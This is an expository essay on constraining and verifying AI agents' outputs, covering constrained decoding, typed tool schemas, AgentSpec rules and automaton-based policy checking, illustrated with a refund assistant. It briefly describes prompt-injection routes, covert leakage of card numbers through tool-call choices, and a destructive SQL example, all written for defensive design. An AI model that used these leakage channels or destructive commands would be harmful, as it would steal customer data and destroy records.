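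Retrying adds little work when failures are rare. *Prove What You Can* combined a provider's JSON enforcement with a check afterwards, and only 34 of 4,085 responses needed correction. Weak models benefit more from constraints. Mündler and colleagues gave Gemma 2 2B, a small model from Google, 292 programs that did not compile, along with the compiler's error messages. 194 programs still failed to compile after the model repaired them without constraints, compared with 103 when it repaired them with type constraints.

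### When the mask forbids good programs

The proof assumes that the mask permits the right answer. In the terms used for checkers, the constraints must be complete, and for a real programming language they seldom are. *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* (Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues, 2026) tested what happens when they aren't. It used the TypeScript software of Mündler and colleagues and the same six models, but applied the constraints from the first token instead of only after a failure. Each model attempted 159 HumanEval problems ten times at each of three temperatures, which control how randomly the model chooses tokens. The best and worst models also attempted 390 MBPP problems. A program counted as a failure if it took more than 300 seconds or 1,000 tokens.

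Unconstrained generation produced more correct programs than constrained generation in 22 of the 24 combinations of model, problem set and temperature, and the other two showed no significant difference. At temperature 0.1, Qwen-2.5-32B solved 82.3 per cent of the HumanEval problems without constraints and 72.3 per cent with them.

One problem was to count the even and odd palindromes up to n. Without constraints, a model called a function `isPalindrome` and defined it further down, which TypeScript allows. The constraining software did not support calling a function before its definition. After the model wrote `is`, the software blocked the rest of the name, and the model wrote `isNaN` instead, a built-in function that tests whether a value is not a number. The model then wrote a helper function that the program never called. The program compiled but gave wrong answers. In other cases, the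 forced choice sent the model into a loop that ran until the limit. This is the same distortion as in the example with A and B, but worse because the mask removed some of the best continuations.

The constraining software would have rejected 982 of the 4,231 compiling programs that Gemma 2 2B wrote without constraints. Timeouts affected 3.5 per cent of Qwen's constrained programs at temperature 0.1 and account for about a third of its ten-point loss. The rest includes crashes of the constraining software and programs like the one with `isNaN`.

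Biagiola and colleagues then switched to TOML, a format for configuration files that is simple enough for a complete grammar. They counted how often a model produced exactly the right document:

| Model | Free | Complete grammar | No space allowed before "=" |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 2 2B | 31.3% | 48.1% | 28.6% |
| Qwen-2.5-32B | 40.3% | 41.3% | 39.7% |
| Qwen-3-Coder-Next-80B | 62.5% | 62.5% | 1.9% |

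In relative terms, the complete grammar improved the smallest model's result by 54 per cent and the 32-billion-parameter model's by 2.5 per cent. It did not improve the result of the largest model, which already made few syntax errors. Forbidding one optional space then reduced the largest model's correct answers by 97 per cent, while forbidding comments or one of two notations for nested data had almost no effect. The harm evidently depends on how often the model writes what is forbidden, not on how much meaning it carries. A designer can measure this in advance by running the mask's rules over texts the model wrote without constraints and counting the good ones they reject.

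Another remedy is to train the model to write output that the constraints allow. Biagiola and colleagues fine-tuned two models with a reward for programs that the constraining software accepts. On HumanEval, Qwen's constrained score rose from 72.3 to 77.6 per cent, while its unconstrained score stayed at about 82 per cent. Gemma's two scores became equal, but only because its unconstrained score fell from 35.7 to 32.8 per cent. The training problems came from the same sets as the test problems, so the gains on unfamiliar problems may be smaller.

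The two TypeScript studies are compatible, because constraints helped when they applied only to retries after a failure and hurt when they applied to every program. With an incomplete mask, a gatekeeper gets better results by letting the model write freely, checking the result and constraining only the retry.

### Do formats harm reasoning?

*Let Me Speak Freely?* (Tam et al., 2024) reported that models solved fewer reasoning problems when they had to answer in a format such as JSON, and fewer still when the format was stricter. The company dottxt, which makes software for constrained decoding, replied that year that the comparison was unfair. The argument has continued because the instruction to use a format, the mask that enforces it, and the lack of room to reason can each lower accuracy.

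There is a theoretical reason to expect the third. A model does a limited amount of computation for each token, so it solves hard problems by writing out intermediate steps. Banerjee and colleagues proved in 2025 that a grammar allowing only a finite set of answers, with no reasoning before them, shrinks the class of problems a model can solve.

*The Format Tax* (Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick, 2026) measured the effect of asking for a format separately from the effect of enforcing it with a mask. In six open models, asking for a format lowered accuracy by 3.9 points on average, and enforcing it lowered accuracy by another 1.6. Three recent closed models lost almost no accuracy when asked for a format. But one of them, GPT-5.4 nano, lost 59 points on mathematics when a grammar forced it to write XML, because it filled the answer field with placeholders such as a promise to solve the problem.

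Fan (2026), in *Capacity, Not Format*, found that the loss depends on how close a model is to its limits. On hard mathematics problems, Claude Sonnet 4.6 scored about 89 per cent with or without JSON, while Claude Haiku 4.5 fell from 88.7 per cent without it to 52.5 per cent with it. Haiku lost nothing in the tests by Lee and colleagues, whose formats had only a field for reasoning and one for the answer. Fan's much longer schema required a restatement of the problem, known values, an approach and verified steps, and many of Haiku's answers ran out of tokens. The stronger Claude Opus 4.7 also fell, from 96.2 to 91.0 per cent, on competition problems.

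Researchers still disagree about the effect of the mask itself. In *Inference for Reasoning Models*, Verma (2026) attributes the loss to the decoder rather than to the request for a format. Nguyen and colleagues tested eleven open models with the prompt and expected format held fixed, and found that masking matched or beat free generation. Masking helped most when it also ruled out impossible answers, for example by requiring exactly four letters when the task was to join the last letters of four names. These results don't support a general figure for the loss from masking, so a team would have to test its own model with its own format.

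The studies agree much more on the remedy, which is to let the model reason first and format its answer afterwards. Lee and colleagues had models answer freely and then convert the answer. Results improved significantly in 42 of 72 comparisons and worsened in 2, using roughly twice as many tokens. Fan recovered 80 per cent of Haiku's loss with a similar method. Fan's worst result came from an interface that forced GPT-4o mini to answer immediately with a function call, which cut its score from 60 to 10 per cent.

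A gatekeeper can use this remedy without weakening its guarantee. The refund assistant can reason about the broken kettle in ordinary English, as long as the interpreter ignores everything except the tool call at the end.

### Does a smaller language make the model more reliable?

A small output language may help the model as well as the checker. *DSLs Enable Reliable Use of LLMs* (Joshi, 2026) argues this for domain-specific languages (DSLs), small languages built for one kind of task, such as SQL for database queries. Unlike Java, a small language offers few ways to express the same intention, so a handful of examples in the prompt can teach a model to use it. It also usually comes with a validator whose error messages refer to the task, such as "you cannot select an action before choosing a client", which helps the model correct itself.

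Joshi built such a language for testing distributed databases. A model turned an English description of a failure into a short script that names the servers, delays a message and specifies what each client should read. The equivalent Java code also has to manage clocks and data encoding, and a reviewer has to check all of it. Joshi offers worked examples rather than measurements. He limits the claim to languages that stay small and notes that designing and maintaining them takes work.

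Languages like SQL also have the advantage of appearing often in training data. For less familiar languages, Microsoft (2025) reported that the accuracy of coding agents often starts below 20 per cent and reaches up to 85 per cent once developers add selected examples and explicit rules to the prompt. Designers of a new output language should therefore expect to write such examples and rules along with the grammar, and should use familiar notation where possible, including details such as the space before an equals sign.

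## Typed tool calls and fixed lists of actions

Most AI agents act through tools that a developer has defined in advance. Each definition has a name, a description in English and a list of arguments with their types. Model companies call this feature function calling. The developer sends the definitions with the prompt, and together they fix the agent's output language. A refund tool could look like this:

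```
{
  "name": "refund",
  "description": "Refund part or all of an open order",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "order":   { "enum": [4402, 4405, 4409, 4411,
                            4413, 4417, 4420, 4426] },
      "dollars": { "type": "integer", "minimum": 1, "maximum": 100 },
      "reason":  { "enum": ["damaged", "late", "wrong_item"] }
    },
    "required": ["order", "dollars", "reason"],
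    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

The keyword `enum` lists the only values a field may take, and the last line of the schema forbids extra fields.

Agents often get such definitions through the Model Context Protocol (2026), or MCP, an open standard that Anthropic launched in November 2024. Developers download its main software kits nearly half a billion times a month. A program that offers tools, called a server, sends its list of tools on request, and the agent's software, called the client, sends back the calls the model writes. Since July 2026 a definition may use the full vocabulary of JSON Schema, the standard notation for describing JSON data, so a developer can make one field depend on another, for example by requiring a photo number whenever the reason is "damaged". Richer schemas also take more work to check, so the release notes of the Model Context Protocol (2026) advise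 implementers to limit schema depth and validation time.

### Form, arguments and state

Suppose the customer with the broken kettle runs a café and has eight open orders. The shop refunds whole dollars, recognises three reasons and allows each customer at most 100 dollars a day. Its checker has to answer three separate questions about each call:

- Is the call well-formed? It must be valid JSON, name an existing tool and give each required field a value of the right type. A call with `"dollars": "eighty"` fails.
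- Are the arguments permitted? A refund of 500 dollars is well-formed but out of range.
- Is the call allowed in the current state? A refund of 80 dollars on order 4411 is well-formed and in range, but it must fail if the customer paid only 30 dollars for that order, or has already received 50 dollars today.

A program can check a call's form and arguments against a schema using only the text of the call. Checking the state requires the shop's records, and the result can change from one minute to the next.

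Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) requires servers to validate all inputs and sorts failures by how likely the model is to fix them. A malformed request or a call to an unknown tool is a protocol error, which models seldom fix. If a value is out of range or a call breaks a business rule, the server returns an ordinary result explaining the problem, and the client should show that result to the model so it can try again.

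The July revision also made developers responsible for managing state. MCP no longer has sessions, so the protocol doesn't connect one call to the next, and any copy of a server may receive any call. A server that needs to keep data between calls returns a handle, such as a shopping basket number, and the model includes it in later calls. The shop should store the daily refund total in the database under the customer's account, not under a handle, because the model could request a new handle and start again from zero. The check and the payment also have to form a single transaction. Otherwise, if two refunds of 80 dollars reach two copies of the server at the same moment, each copy may find a total of zero and pay.

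Even the schema checks don't always happen by default. Anthropic can enforce a schema through constrained decoding, but only for part of JSON Schema, according to its *Strict tool use*. For research-hub's *Measuring tool input schema fidelity*, Ola Hungerford tested 24 models on six tools whose schemas use more demanding keywords, running each model with each tool 20 times. Most combinations worked every time. But Anthropic's interface rejected a schema that required exactly one of two fields, and two Gemini models filled some fields with display labels instead of the permitted values. MCP's TypeScript and Python kits did not validate the current version of JSON Schema correctly until the developer added a separate validator. A shop should run its own validator on the server and test it with invalid calls.

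What the software does after a failed check also matters. *A DbC Inspired Neurosymbolic Layer for Trustworthy Agent Design* (Leoveanu-Condrei, 2025) describes a layer that wraps model calls in contracts, which combine type validation with programmer-written conditions on the content. If an output fails, the model tries to repair it. If the repair fails too, the layer can return the raw output anyway. This may suit a chatbot that must always answer, but in a refund tool the same fallback would let through requests that had failed the check.

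### 2,400 possible calls

With eight orders, 100 amounts and three reasons, the model can write 8 × 100 × 3 = 2,400 different refund calls. Picking one takes about 11 bits of information, since 2^11 is 2,048. A test program can try every call on a copy of the shop's records and list the ones the checker accepts.

Suppose the orders cost 20, 30, 45, 60, 80, 100, 150 and 200 dollars, and the customer has had no refund yet. There are then 20 + 30 + 45 + 60 + 80 + 100 + 100 + 100 = 535 permitted amounts, and with three possible reasons for each, 1,605 permitted calls. If the checker accepts 1,606 calls, it has a bug, and the list of accepted calls includes one it should have rejected.

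This count covers single calls. Two calls in a row already allow 5.76 million combinations, and three allow almost 14 billion. But checking the daily limit requires only the total paid out by earlier calls, which has 101 possible values, from 0 to 100. Testing every call against every total takes 242,400 trials, which a computer can still run quickly.

Now suppose the shop adds a field for a 200-character note to the customer. An English keyboard has 95 printable characters, so each character adds about 6.6 bits and the whole note about 1,300. That makes more than 10^395 possible notes, too many for any computer to go through. The checker can still limit the length, forbid links and search for particular words, but it can't reliably detect whether a note promises a second refund or reveals another customer's address. The limit on the amount still holds as long as no program acts on the note.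 If another AI agent reads the note, it can carry a prompt injection.

Short calls can also leak information, though slowly. A 16-digit card number contains about 53 bits, so a hijacked assistant would need five refunds to leak one through its choice of orders, amounts and reasons. A single note could hold a dozen card numbers.

### Replacing strings with references, enumerations and ranges

A designer who wants checkable calls should therefore replace free strings with references, enumerations and ranges wherever the task allows it. Each replacement takes something away from the agent:

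| Free string | Replacement | What the agent can no longer do |
|---|---|---|
| Recipient's email address | Order number, from which the server looks up the address | Write to a new address |
| Note to the customer | One of 20 approved messages | Answer an unusual complaint |
| Delivery date | Whole number of days from 1 to 14 | Promise "before the wedding" |
| Database query | Named query with typed arguments | Ask a question nobody foresaw |

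A reference is an identifier that the server resolves from its own records. An injected instruction may still lead the model to choose the wrong order, but it can't introduce a stranger's email address. The server also has to check, on every call, that the customer is allowed to use the order. Under MCP's guidance on handles, too, knowing an object's name shouldn't give the caller a right to it.

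An enumeration needs an option such as "other", which passes the case to an employee. Without it, the model has to choose a wrong reason when none of the listed reasons fits, and the shop records kettles that arrived late as damaged.

One badly chosen field can undo the benefits of typing a tool call. MCP's documentation includes an example tool called `execute_sql`, which takes a region and a database query, both as plain strings. The query field accepts `DELETE FROM customers` as readily as `SELECT name FROM customers`. A tool that accepts shell commands has the same problem. The call is still typed, but the string inside it is written in a far richer language, which the checker now has to analyze.

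This also limits what a company can control by tool name. MCP now puts the tool's name in a header of each request, so that a gateway can authorize calls without reading the rest of the request. That works for `refund`, whose possible effects the shop knows, but permission to use `execute_sql` may let the caller do anything to the database. The shop can limit the damage by giving the tool a database account that can only read certain tables, so that the database enforces a restriction that the tool's schema can't.

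### AgentSpec and rules for single actions

Some rules apply to many tools at once, such as asking an employee before any large payment. Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, designed a small language that keeps such rules separate from the tools. Each rule has an event that triggers it, conditions to check and a response. A rule for the shop could look like this:

```
rule @inspect_large_refund
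trigger refund
check
    amount_above(50)
enforce
    user_inspection
end
```

Before the agent carries out a refund, the AgentSpec software tests the rule's condition. If the condition holds, a person has to confirm the call. A rule can instead stop the agent, carry out a preset action or make the model reconsider. A manager can read such a rule, but someone still has to write and test each condition as a Python function. AgentSpec allows any call that no rule applies to, whereas Amazon's policy language Cedar denies any request that no policy permits.

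AgentSpec's rules stopped a simulated household robot from completing any of the hazardous instructions in a test. Without the rules, the robot carried out hazardous instructions in nine of ten categories, and in the worst category it completed 79 per cent of them. The rules also reduced its success on safe tasks from 58.6 to 54.3 per cent. A single rule covered 96 risky scenarios by forbidding the robot to pour liquid onto anything outside a list of objects that may get wet. Testing a condition took about a millisecond. However, the researchers wrote the rules from descriptions of the dangers in the test, so the result applies only to hazards that someone had foreseen.

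The results were weaker for an agent that wrote Python. It tried to run 422 programs in response to risky requests, and the rules flagged 333 of them. The researchers inspected these and let 58 through as harmless. The rules missed the other 89, but in 58 of those the agent had left out the flaw it was asked to include. The rules caught only 3 of 25 programs with side-channel flaws, which reveal secrets indirectly, for example through timing.

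The difference comes largely from what the conditions can inspect. A pouring action specifies its target, so the condition only has to look up that object in a list. For Python, the conditions search the source text for suspicious commands, and a program can evade this search as easily as a shell script can. Wang and colleagues describe the search as an initial safeguard and suggest that tracking data flow would make it more accurate.

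Rules written by OpenAI's o1 model stopped 87 per cent of the risky code but prevented traffic violations in only five of eight driving scenarios, while the handwritten rules prevented them in all eight. One of o1's household rules banned pouring altogether, so the robot couldn't water the plants.

Blocking a bad call doesn't complete the task either. In simulated customer transactions, *The Verifier Tax* (2026) found that checks before each action intercepted violations in up to 94 per cent of episodes, but agents often failed to find an acceptable alternative in the turns they had left. Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026) report in *Toward Safe LLM Agents* that agents in the same study completed fewer than 5 per cent of tasks both safely and correctly in most settings. They give this evidence their lowest certainty rating because it comes from one study. Still, a shop should measure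 how many customers get the right refund as well as how many wrong refunds it blocks.

Rules that check one call at a time can also miss harm that builds up over several calls. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) warns that planted instructions can steer an agent through a sequence of calls that are ordinary on their own but harmful together. For example, the assistant may be allowed to read a customer's address and to email a supplier, but not to email the supplier that address. To catch this, the checker needs rules that take earlier calls into account.

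### From tool calls to code

Many agents now write programs that call tools, instead of making one JSON call at a time. *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2024) made an early case for this with a system called CodeAct. A Python program can store one tool's result, pass it to another tool and repeat the steps for every item in a list. Models had also seen a lot of Python in training. On 82 tasks that typically needed several tools, the best of the 17 models, a version of GPT-4, solved 74 per cent with Python and 52 per cent with JSON. With Python, it also needed about two fewer turns per task.

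Token use was another reason to have agents write code instead of making ordinary tool calls. If an agent copies the transcript of a two-hour meeting from one service to another with ordinary tool calls, the text passes through the model twice, which can add 50,000 tokens. In November 2025 Anthropic proposed that agents write code that moves such data directly and load only the tool definitions they need. In its example, this reduced the total from 150,000 tokens to 2,000. Moving data with code can also keep private data out of the model's context.

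Anthropic has since built tool calling through code into its own service. According to Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling*, code improved results on web research tests by 11 per cent on average and used 24 per cent fewer input tokens. On a project-management test with 75 tools, it cut input tokens by about 38 per cent without changing accuracy. On simulated customer service for airlines, shops and telephone companies, where the agent makes only one or two calls per turn, code did not improve results and cost about 8 per cent more.

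*The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) compared writing tool calls as code and as JSON, on 309 tasks with 14 models. Code did at least as well as JSON with 11 of the models, but its average over all 14 was slightly lower, at 77.0 per cent against 78.6. This was because three older OpenAI models wrote line breaks incorrectly and their longer scripts crashed. Without those three, code averages 82 per cent and JSON 78. Code helped most when a task needed many calls. With JSON, Claude Sonnet 5 made every required call when a task needed up to 70 at once but failed completely at 100, while with code it still made all 100.

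The tools in this test only returned the arguments they received. It therefore measured whether models could write the right calls, and not whether they could handle real results. That leaves out much of what makes scripts hard to check, as in this one:

```
for order in open_orders():
    if order.days_late > 7:
        refund(order.id, 20, "late")
```

The number of refunds the script issues depends on the shop's records. In Anthropic's system, the script pauses at each tool call and the developer's software receives the call as typed data, so the shop can still check every refund. If all eight orders are late, the daily limit stops the sixth refund, after the first five have paid out 100 dollars. However, an employee who approves the script in advance must understand a program instead of a single amount.

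Calling tools from code also removes some protections. Anthropic's strict mode doesn't work for these calls, so the developer has to validate them separately. The script needs limits on its use of resources and a sandbox, a closed environment that restricts what it can reach. Anthropic acknowledges that direct tool calls avoid these burdens. It also warns that tool results arrive as strings, which may contain text written by a stranger. If a script runs part of a result as code, it can execute that text.

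### When to allow code

Fixed calls are the better choice for a refund desk because the tasks are short, code brings little or no gain, and the shop can test every call. The case for code is much stronger when an agent has to check the expenses of 20 employees, which may run to thousands of line items. With single calls, the model has to request and read each employee's records in turn. The developer could add a special tool for this question, but the next question may need another one. A developer who keeps adding tools to imitate loops and conditions ends up designing a programming language.

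The security of code that calls typed tools depends mainly on what else the code can reach. If the tools are its only way to change anything outside the sandbox, the checker can inspect every call that could do so. If the code can also install packages or open network connections, the tool schemas cover only part of what the agent can do. CodeAct's agents could download data and use existing Python packages, which made them more capable but left much of their behaviour outside any list of tools.

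Some designs allow more than fixed calls but less than unrestricted code. Examples include small languages for writing plans, and type systems that limit which data and tools the code may use.

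## Policies written as finite automata

An AI can write down in advance what an agent should do in every situation, instead of proposing one call at a time. If it writes this policy as a finite automaton, a checker can examine every sequence of actions the policy allows before the agent is used. The interpreter then follows the automaton, so the language model no longer chooses the next step.

### A controller and a rule

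A controller of this kind has a finite set of states, one of which is the starting state, together with a set of observations, a set of actions and a list of transitions. Each transition fixes the action and the next state for one combination of state and observation. Suppose the shop confirms a customer's identity by sending a code to the phone number on the account. Its refund assistant could follow this controller:

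| State | Observation | Action | Next state |
|---|---|---|---|
| Start | Code correct | None | Verified |
| Start | Code wrong | Ask again | Start |
| Start | Customer leaves | None | Closed |
| Verified | Claim accepted | Refund | Refunded |
| Verified | Claim rejected | Explain why | Closed |
| Refunded | Payment confirmed | Send receipt | Closed |

Any other observation changes nothing.

A second automaton encodes the rule that identity verification must come before any refund. It takes no actions and only tracks events, starting in the Locked state. A correct code moves it to Unlocked, where it stays. A refund while it is Locked moves it to Violation, where it also stays.

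The checker runs the two automata side by side by building their product, whose states are pairs of a controller state and a rule state. Four controller states and three rule states give 12 pairs, but only some of them can occur. A simple search finds them:

1. The checker starts from the pair (Start, Locked).
2. From each pair it has found, it follows every transition of the controller and works out how the same observation and action change the rule's state.
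3. If this leads to a new pair, it adds the pair to its list and notes which pair it came from.
4. It stops when it reaches a pair that contains Violation, or when no new pairs turn up.

For this controller, the search finds five pairs:

```
(Start, Locked)
(Verified, Unlocked)
(Refunded, Unlocked)
(Closed, Locked)
(Closed, Unlocked)
```

None of the five pairs contains Violation, so no conversation can lead to a refund before the customer enters a correct code. A customer can enter a wrong code any number of times, so there are infinitely many possible conversations, but they all stay within these five pairs.

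Now suppose the AI adds one transition so that customers can reopen a case: if a customer writes again, the controller moves from Closed to Verified. This works for customers who entered their code earlier, and a tester may well try only those. The search, however, reaches a pair with Violation. By following its notes back to the start, the checker produces a counterexample:

```
(Start, Locked)          customer leaves
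(Closed, Locked)         customer writes again
(Verified, Locked)       claim accepted, refund
(Refunded, Violation)
```

A stranger could get a refund by opening a chat, leaving and coming back. Sending reopened cases to Start fixes the controller, and the search then finds six pairs and no violation. But a customer can still reopen a case, enter another code and collect a second refund. The rule doesn't forbid that, so the shop needs another rule automaton that moves to Violation at the second refund on the same case.

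### Rules in temporal logic

People usually write such rules as formulas and let software build the automaton. The standard notation is linear temporal logic, which adds "always", "next", "eventually" and "until" to "and", "or" and "not". The refund rule becomes "no refund until code correct". The strong version of "until" also requires that a correct code eventually arrive. The controller would fail this requirement because the customer may leave before entering one, so the shop needs the weak version, which doesn't include it.

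A rule such as "every case eventually closes" needs a different search. No single step can break it, because the case might still close later. The model checker therefore looks for a loop in which the controller can stay forever without closing the case. The refund controller has several such loops, including one in which a customer keeps entering wrong codes. A limit of three attempts removes that loop, but the controller then needs a separate state for each attempt, because its state is its only memory.

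### How language models write automata

A group around Yunhao Yang and Ufuk Topcu at the University of Texas at Austin has worked on this since GPT-3. In *Automaton-Based Representations of Task Knowledge from Generative Language Models* (2022), Yang, Gaglione and colleagues prompted GPT-3 for the numbered steps of a task such as crossing a road. An ordinary program then turned each step into a state. The verb phrase in a step becomes an action that leads to the next state, unless a word such as "if", "wait" or "until" marks it as a condition. For example, "if no car, cross" produces two transitions. If there is no car, the controller crosses and moves to the next state. Otherwise it does nothing and stays in the same state. Because GPT-3 may word the same action differently in different steps, such as "cross the road" and "walk across the road", the program also asks it whether each pair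 of phrases means the same thing and merges the pairs for which it answers yes.

To check a controller, the researchers add a third automaton that models the environment, such as a traffic light that changes colour in a fixed order. The product combines the states of the controller and the environment and leaves out sequences that the environment cannot produce. If nobody knows which changes are possible, the model can allow all of them. The check then misses nothing, but it takes longer and raises more false alarms.

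*Fine-Tuning Language Models Using Formal Methods Feedback* (Yang, Bhatt and colleagues, 2023) used a model checker's results as training data. Llama 2 7B, a small open model, wrote several sets of instructions for each driving task. Software converted each set into a controller, and the model checker NuSMV tested the controller against 15 traffic rules. If one set satisfied more rules than another, the two became a training pair of a better and a worse answer, so nobody had to label the data by hand. Training on about 3,000 pairs raised the share of rules that the controllers satisfied from 60 to over 90 per cent.

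One counterexample involved a right turn at a traffic light. The original model's instructions were to check the light, look for cars from the left, look for pedestrians and then turn. NuSMV found a sequence in which the light turns red and a car arrives from the left while the vehicle is checking for pedestrians, so the vehicle turns into the car's path. The fine-tuned model's instructions check for cars and pedestrians together, just before the turn. The researchers doubt that a human inspector would have noticed the problem.

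The result for left turns is less reassuring. The fine-tuned model's instructions were to turn if the left-turn light is green and otherwise stop. The controller passed all 15 rules, one of which forbids turning while a car is coming from the left. But it never checks for cars, so it can pass only if the model of the junction contains no such car while the left-turn light is green. At a real junction, there might be one because a driver ran a red light. Yang and colleagues proved that a verified controller obeys the rules in reality if the environment model includes every change that can happen there, and they acknowledge that the guarantee does not hold otherwise.

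The rules need the same care. One of the 15 required the car to stop "eventually" after it sees a pedestrian. A car could satisfy this by driving past the pedestrian and stopping at the next junction.

### Improving the text instead of the model

The group's later systems do not change the model's weights. *LAD-VF* (Yang, Hong and colleagues, 2025) had a language model rewrite the prompt in response to the rule violations that NuSMV found. GPT-4o then wrote controllers directly in NuSMV's input language. On test tasks, these controllers satisfied 86 per cent of the rules on average, compared with 98 per cent after fine-tuning and 1 per cent when the prompt only stated the rules. The rewritten prompts carried over better to other robots. When the researchers switched from an outdoor robot to an indoor one, the score fell from 90 to 88 per cent with rewritten prompts and from 90 to 63 per cent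 with the fine-tuned model. The 86 per cent average came from tests with three rules, and the score fell to 71 per cent with ten.

*VASO* (Yang, Bhatt and colleagues, 2026) applied the idea to robot skills, which are reusable instructions for tasks such as driving around an obstacle. GPT-5-nano writes the skill, and GPT-4o-mini uses it to write plans. Software first checks that the skill's goal doesn't contradict the safety rules. Of the new skills, 89 per cent passed, and 97 per cent did after one revision. If a plan later breaks a rule, GPT-5-nano receives the broken rule and revises the skill, so that future plans benefit too. In tests with a ground robot and a drone, plans reached 97.2 per cent compliance with 11 rules. The rule about people was stricter than in 2023, requiring the robot to stop in the very next step.

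A gatekeeper can reject a plan that breaks even one of the 11 rules and let the model try again. With this check in place, these percentages indicate how many attempts the model will need, not how safe the accepted plans are.

This works only if the automaton that passes the check is the one that runs. In *Bridging LLM Planning Agents and Formal Methods*, Ramani, Tawosi and colleagues (2025) had language models translate existing English plans and their goals into NuSMV's language. With GPT-5's translations, NuSMV judged 95.9 per cent of the plans correctly, excluding the 7 per cent for which it gave no verdict. GPT-5 judged 99.6 per cent correctly when it assessed the plans directly. Some of GPT-5's translations passed the check without fully reflecting the plan's intent, so passing proved nothing about the plan itself. A model should therefore write the automaton that the interpreter will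 execute, rather than a description of a separate plan.

Translating requirements into formal language is also hard. Dantas and colleagues report that, on one benchmark, only 24.8 to 34.2 per cent of language models' translations from English into a standard planning language had the right meaning. If a model also writes the rules, someone has to review them.

### Agentproof and workflow graphs

Many developers already write agents as graphs. Each node is a model call, a tool or a request for human approval, and the arrows determine which steps can follow which. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) presents a checker that extracts these graphs from four popular frameworks, including LangGraph and CrewAI. The checker compiles each rule into an automaton and searches the product of the graph and the automaton, as in the refund example. If a path breaks the rule, the checker returns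 that path.

Agentproof doesn't check the free text that the model writes inside a node. When the model chooses between branches, the search treats every branch as possible. The search is therefore sound, but it is incomplete because some of those paths never occur in practice.

Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 workflows and 15 rules of their own. It found structural defects in five workflows, such as an email-drafting step with no arrow to the sending step. Ten workflows lacked a human approval step. In one workflow, the search found an email draft without the required review, which ten random test runs had missed. The structural checks took about a tenth of a second on a graph of 5,000 nodes; the test workflows had 5 to 12. The researchers designed the workflows to contain defects, so the counts are evidence of what the tool can find but don't measure how common such defects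 are.

Agentproof's rules also show how easily a formal rule can fail to enforce what it was meant to. Its rule language has seven forms, none of which directly expresses "no refund until code correct". A rule called "Deploy approval" requires an approval after each deployment of new software, although a company would normally want one before it. As Xavier and colleagues define this form, the automaton signals a violation only if a second deployment happens without an approval in between, so an agent that deploys once and never gets approval would pass.

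A separate check, better suited to this purpose, removes all human approval steps from the graph and tests whether any path still leads to a sensitive tool. If one does, the agent can use the tool without approval. But the software identifies human steps in LangGraph by the word "human" in their names. It will miss an approval step called "manager_review", and it could treat a model call named "humanize_text" as one.

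### Policy extraction and shields

Some policies start out as neural networks that learn by trial and error, and nobody can check these networks the way they could check a table of transitions. In 2018 Osbert Bastani, Yewen Pu and Armando Solar-Lezama presented VIPER, which trains a decision tree to imitate such a network. A decision tree is a series of yes-or-no questions about the situation that ends in an action. VIPER lets the tree act, records what the network would have done in the same situations, and retrains the tree with the most weight on situations where a wrong action would do the most harm. It produced a tree that provably never loses at a toy version of the video game Pong. In the same year, Gail Weiss, Yoav Goldberg and Eran Yahav extracted finite automata from neural networks that read sequences.

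A proof about an extracted tree or automaton doesn't cover the network it imitates, so the extracted version has to replace the network for the proof to apply. The replacement may perform worse, because a small tree cannot reproduce everything a large network has learned.

A shield, by contrast, lets the network choose actions and overrides only the unsafe ones. Alshiekh, Bloem, Topcu and colleagues described shields for learning agents in 2018. The construction starts from the product of a rule automaton and a model of the environment, where each state is a pair of their states. It marks every pair that contains a violation as lost. It then marks each pair in which every available action could lead to a lost pair, and repeats this step until it finds no more. Every remaining pair has at least one safe action, and the shield blocks the unsafe ones.

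The repetition lets the shield act early enough. If a robot needs two metres to stop, the shield makes it brake at least two metres before a staircase. A filter that only forbids driving over the edge would react too late. For the refund assistant, the shield only has to block refunds while the rule automaton is Locked.

Shields suit language models because the model can choose freely among the safe actions and doesn't have to write a complete controller. But shields, like checks on single tool calls, don't ensure that the agent finishes its task. Most of the evidence on language-model agents concerns simpler monitors. Dantas and colleagues cite a study of household agents in which monitoring reduced unsafe actions by 65 per cent, and note that such monitors' guarantees cover only single steps or short sequences.

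### Too many states

An environment model may need a state for every combination of yes-or-no facts, such as whether a pedestrian is in front, and thirty such facts give about a billion states. The state counts of separate controllers running at the same time also multiply, so ten copies of the four-state refund controller have about a million joint states. NuSMV can handle far more states than it could list one by one, because it represents sets of states as formulas, but this doesn't help with every system. Bhatt, Yang and colleagues (2024), in *Know Where You're Uncertain When Planning with Multimodal Foundation Models*, considered model checking too slow to run while a robot is planning, so they ran it beforehand on sample plans and used the results to estimate how likely a new plan was to satisfy the rules.

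Tracking amounts of money adds states even faster. If the refund controller had to enforce the daily limit itself, it would need 404 states, one for each combination of its four current states and the 101 possible totals. Tracking separate totals for eight orders would require about 10^16 combinations. The shop should therefore leave the totals to the checker for tool calls and use the automaton only for the order of steps. A finite automaton also can't count without limit, so it can't enforce a rule such as "never send out more replacements than customers have returned".

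### From images and messages to symbols

The proof starts from symbols such as "pedestrian" or "code correct" and does not cover how the system arrives at them. If an object detector misses one pedestrian in fifty, a verified controller can drive into that pedestrian. Yang and colleagues argued in 2023 that their driving controllers would keep their guarantee on real roads because a detector was about as accurate on real images as on simulated ones, but a detector with similar accuracy in both settings can still miss pedestrians in both. In VASO, a language model also writes the functions that translate the robot's readings and commands into symbols. Plans scored about as well with these functions as with handwritten ones, but nobody verifies the functions, and Yang and colleagues acknowledge that a mistake in them can invalidate the guarantee.

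Bhatt and colleagues tried to measure this risk. They ran a detector on 542 images from a driving simulator with about 3,000 known objects, and used its errors to convert its confidence into a lower bound on the probability that it is right. If the bound for a new image is below 70 per cent, the robot looks again. Each plan gets a similar score for how likely it is to satisfy the rules. In 50 real driving scenes, four plans broke a rule, and all four scored below 70 per cent, so withholding low-scoring plans would have prevented every violation. These statistical bounds hold only if new scenes resemble the calibration images. With at most 46 plans left, zero violations is also compatible with a true violation rate of about 6 per cent.

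Text raises the same problem. In the refund controller, the symbol "code correct" comes from an exact comparison of two numbers, while "claim accepted" may come from a language model reading the customer's message. An instruction injected into that message can lead the model to accept a false claim, but it can't change the result of the code comparison. The shop should therefore base its most important rules on symbols that ordinary software can compute exactly.

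## Plans in a small language, checked before they run

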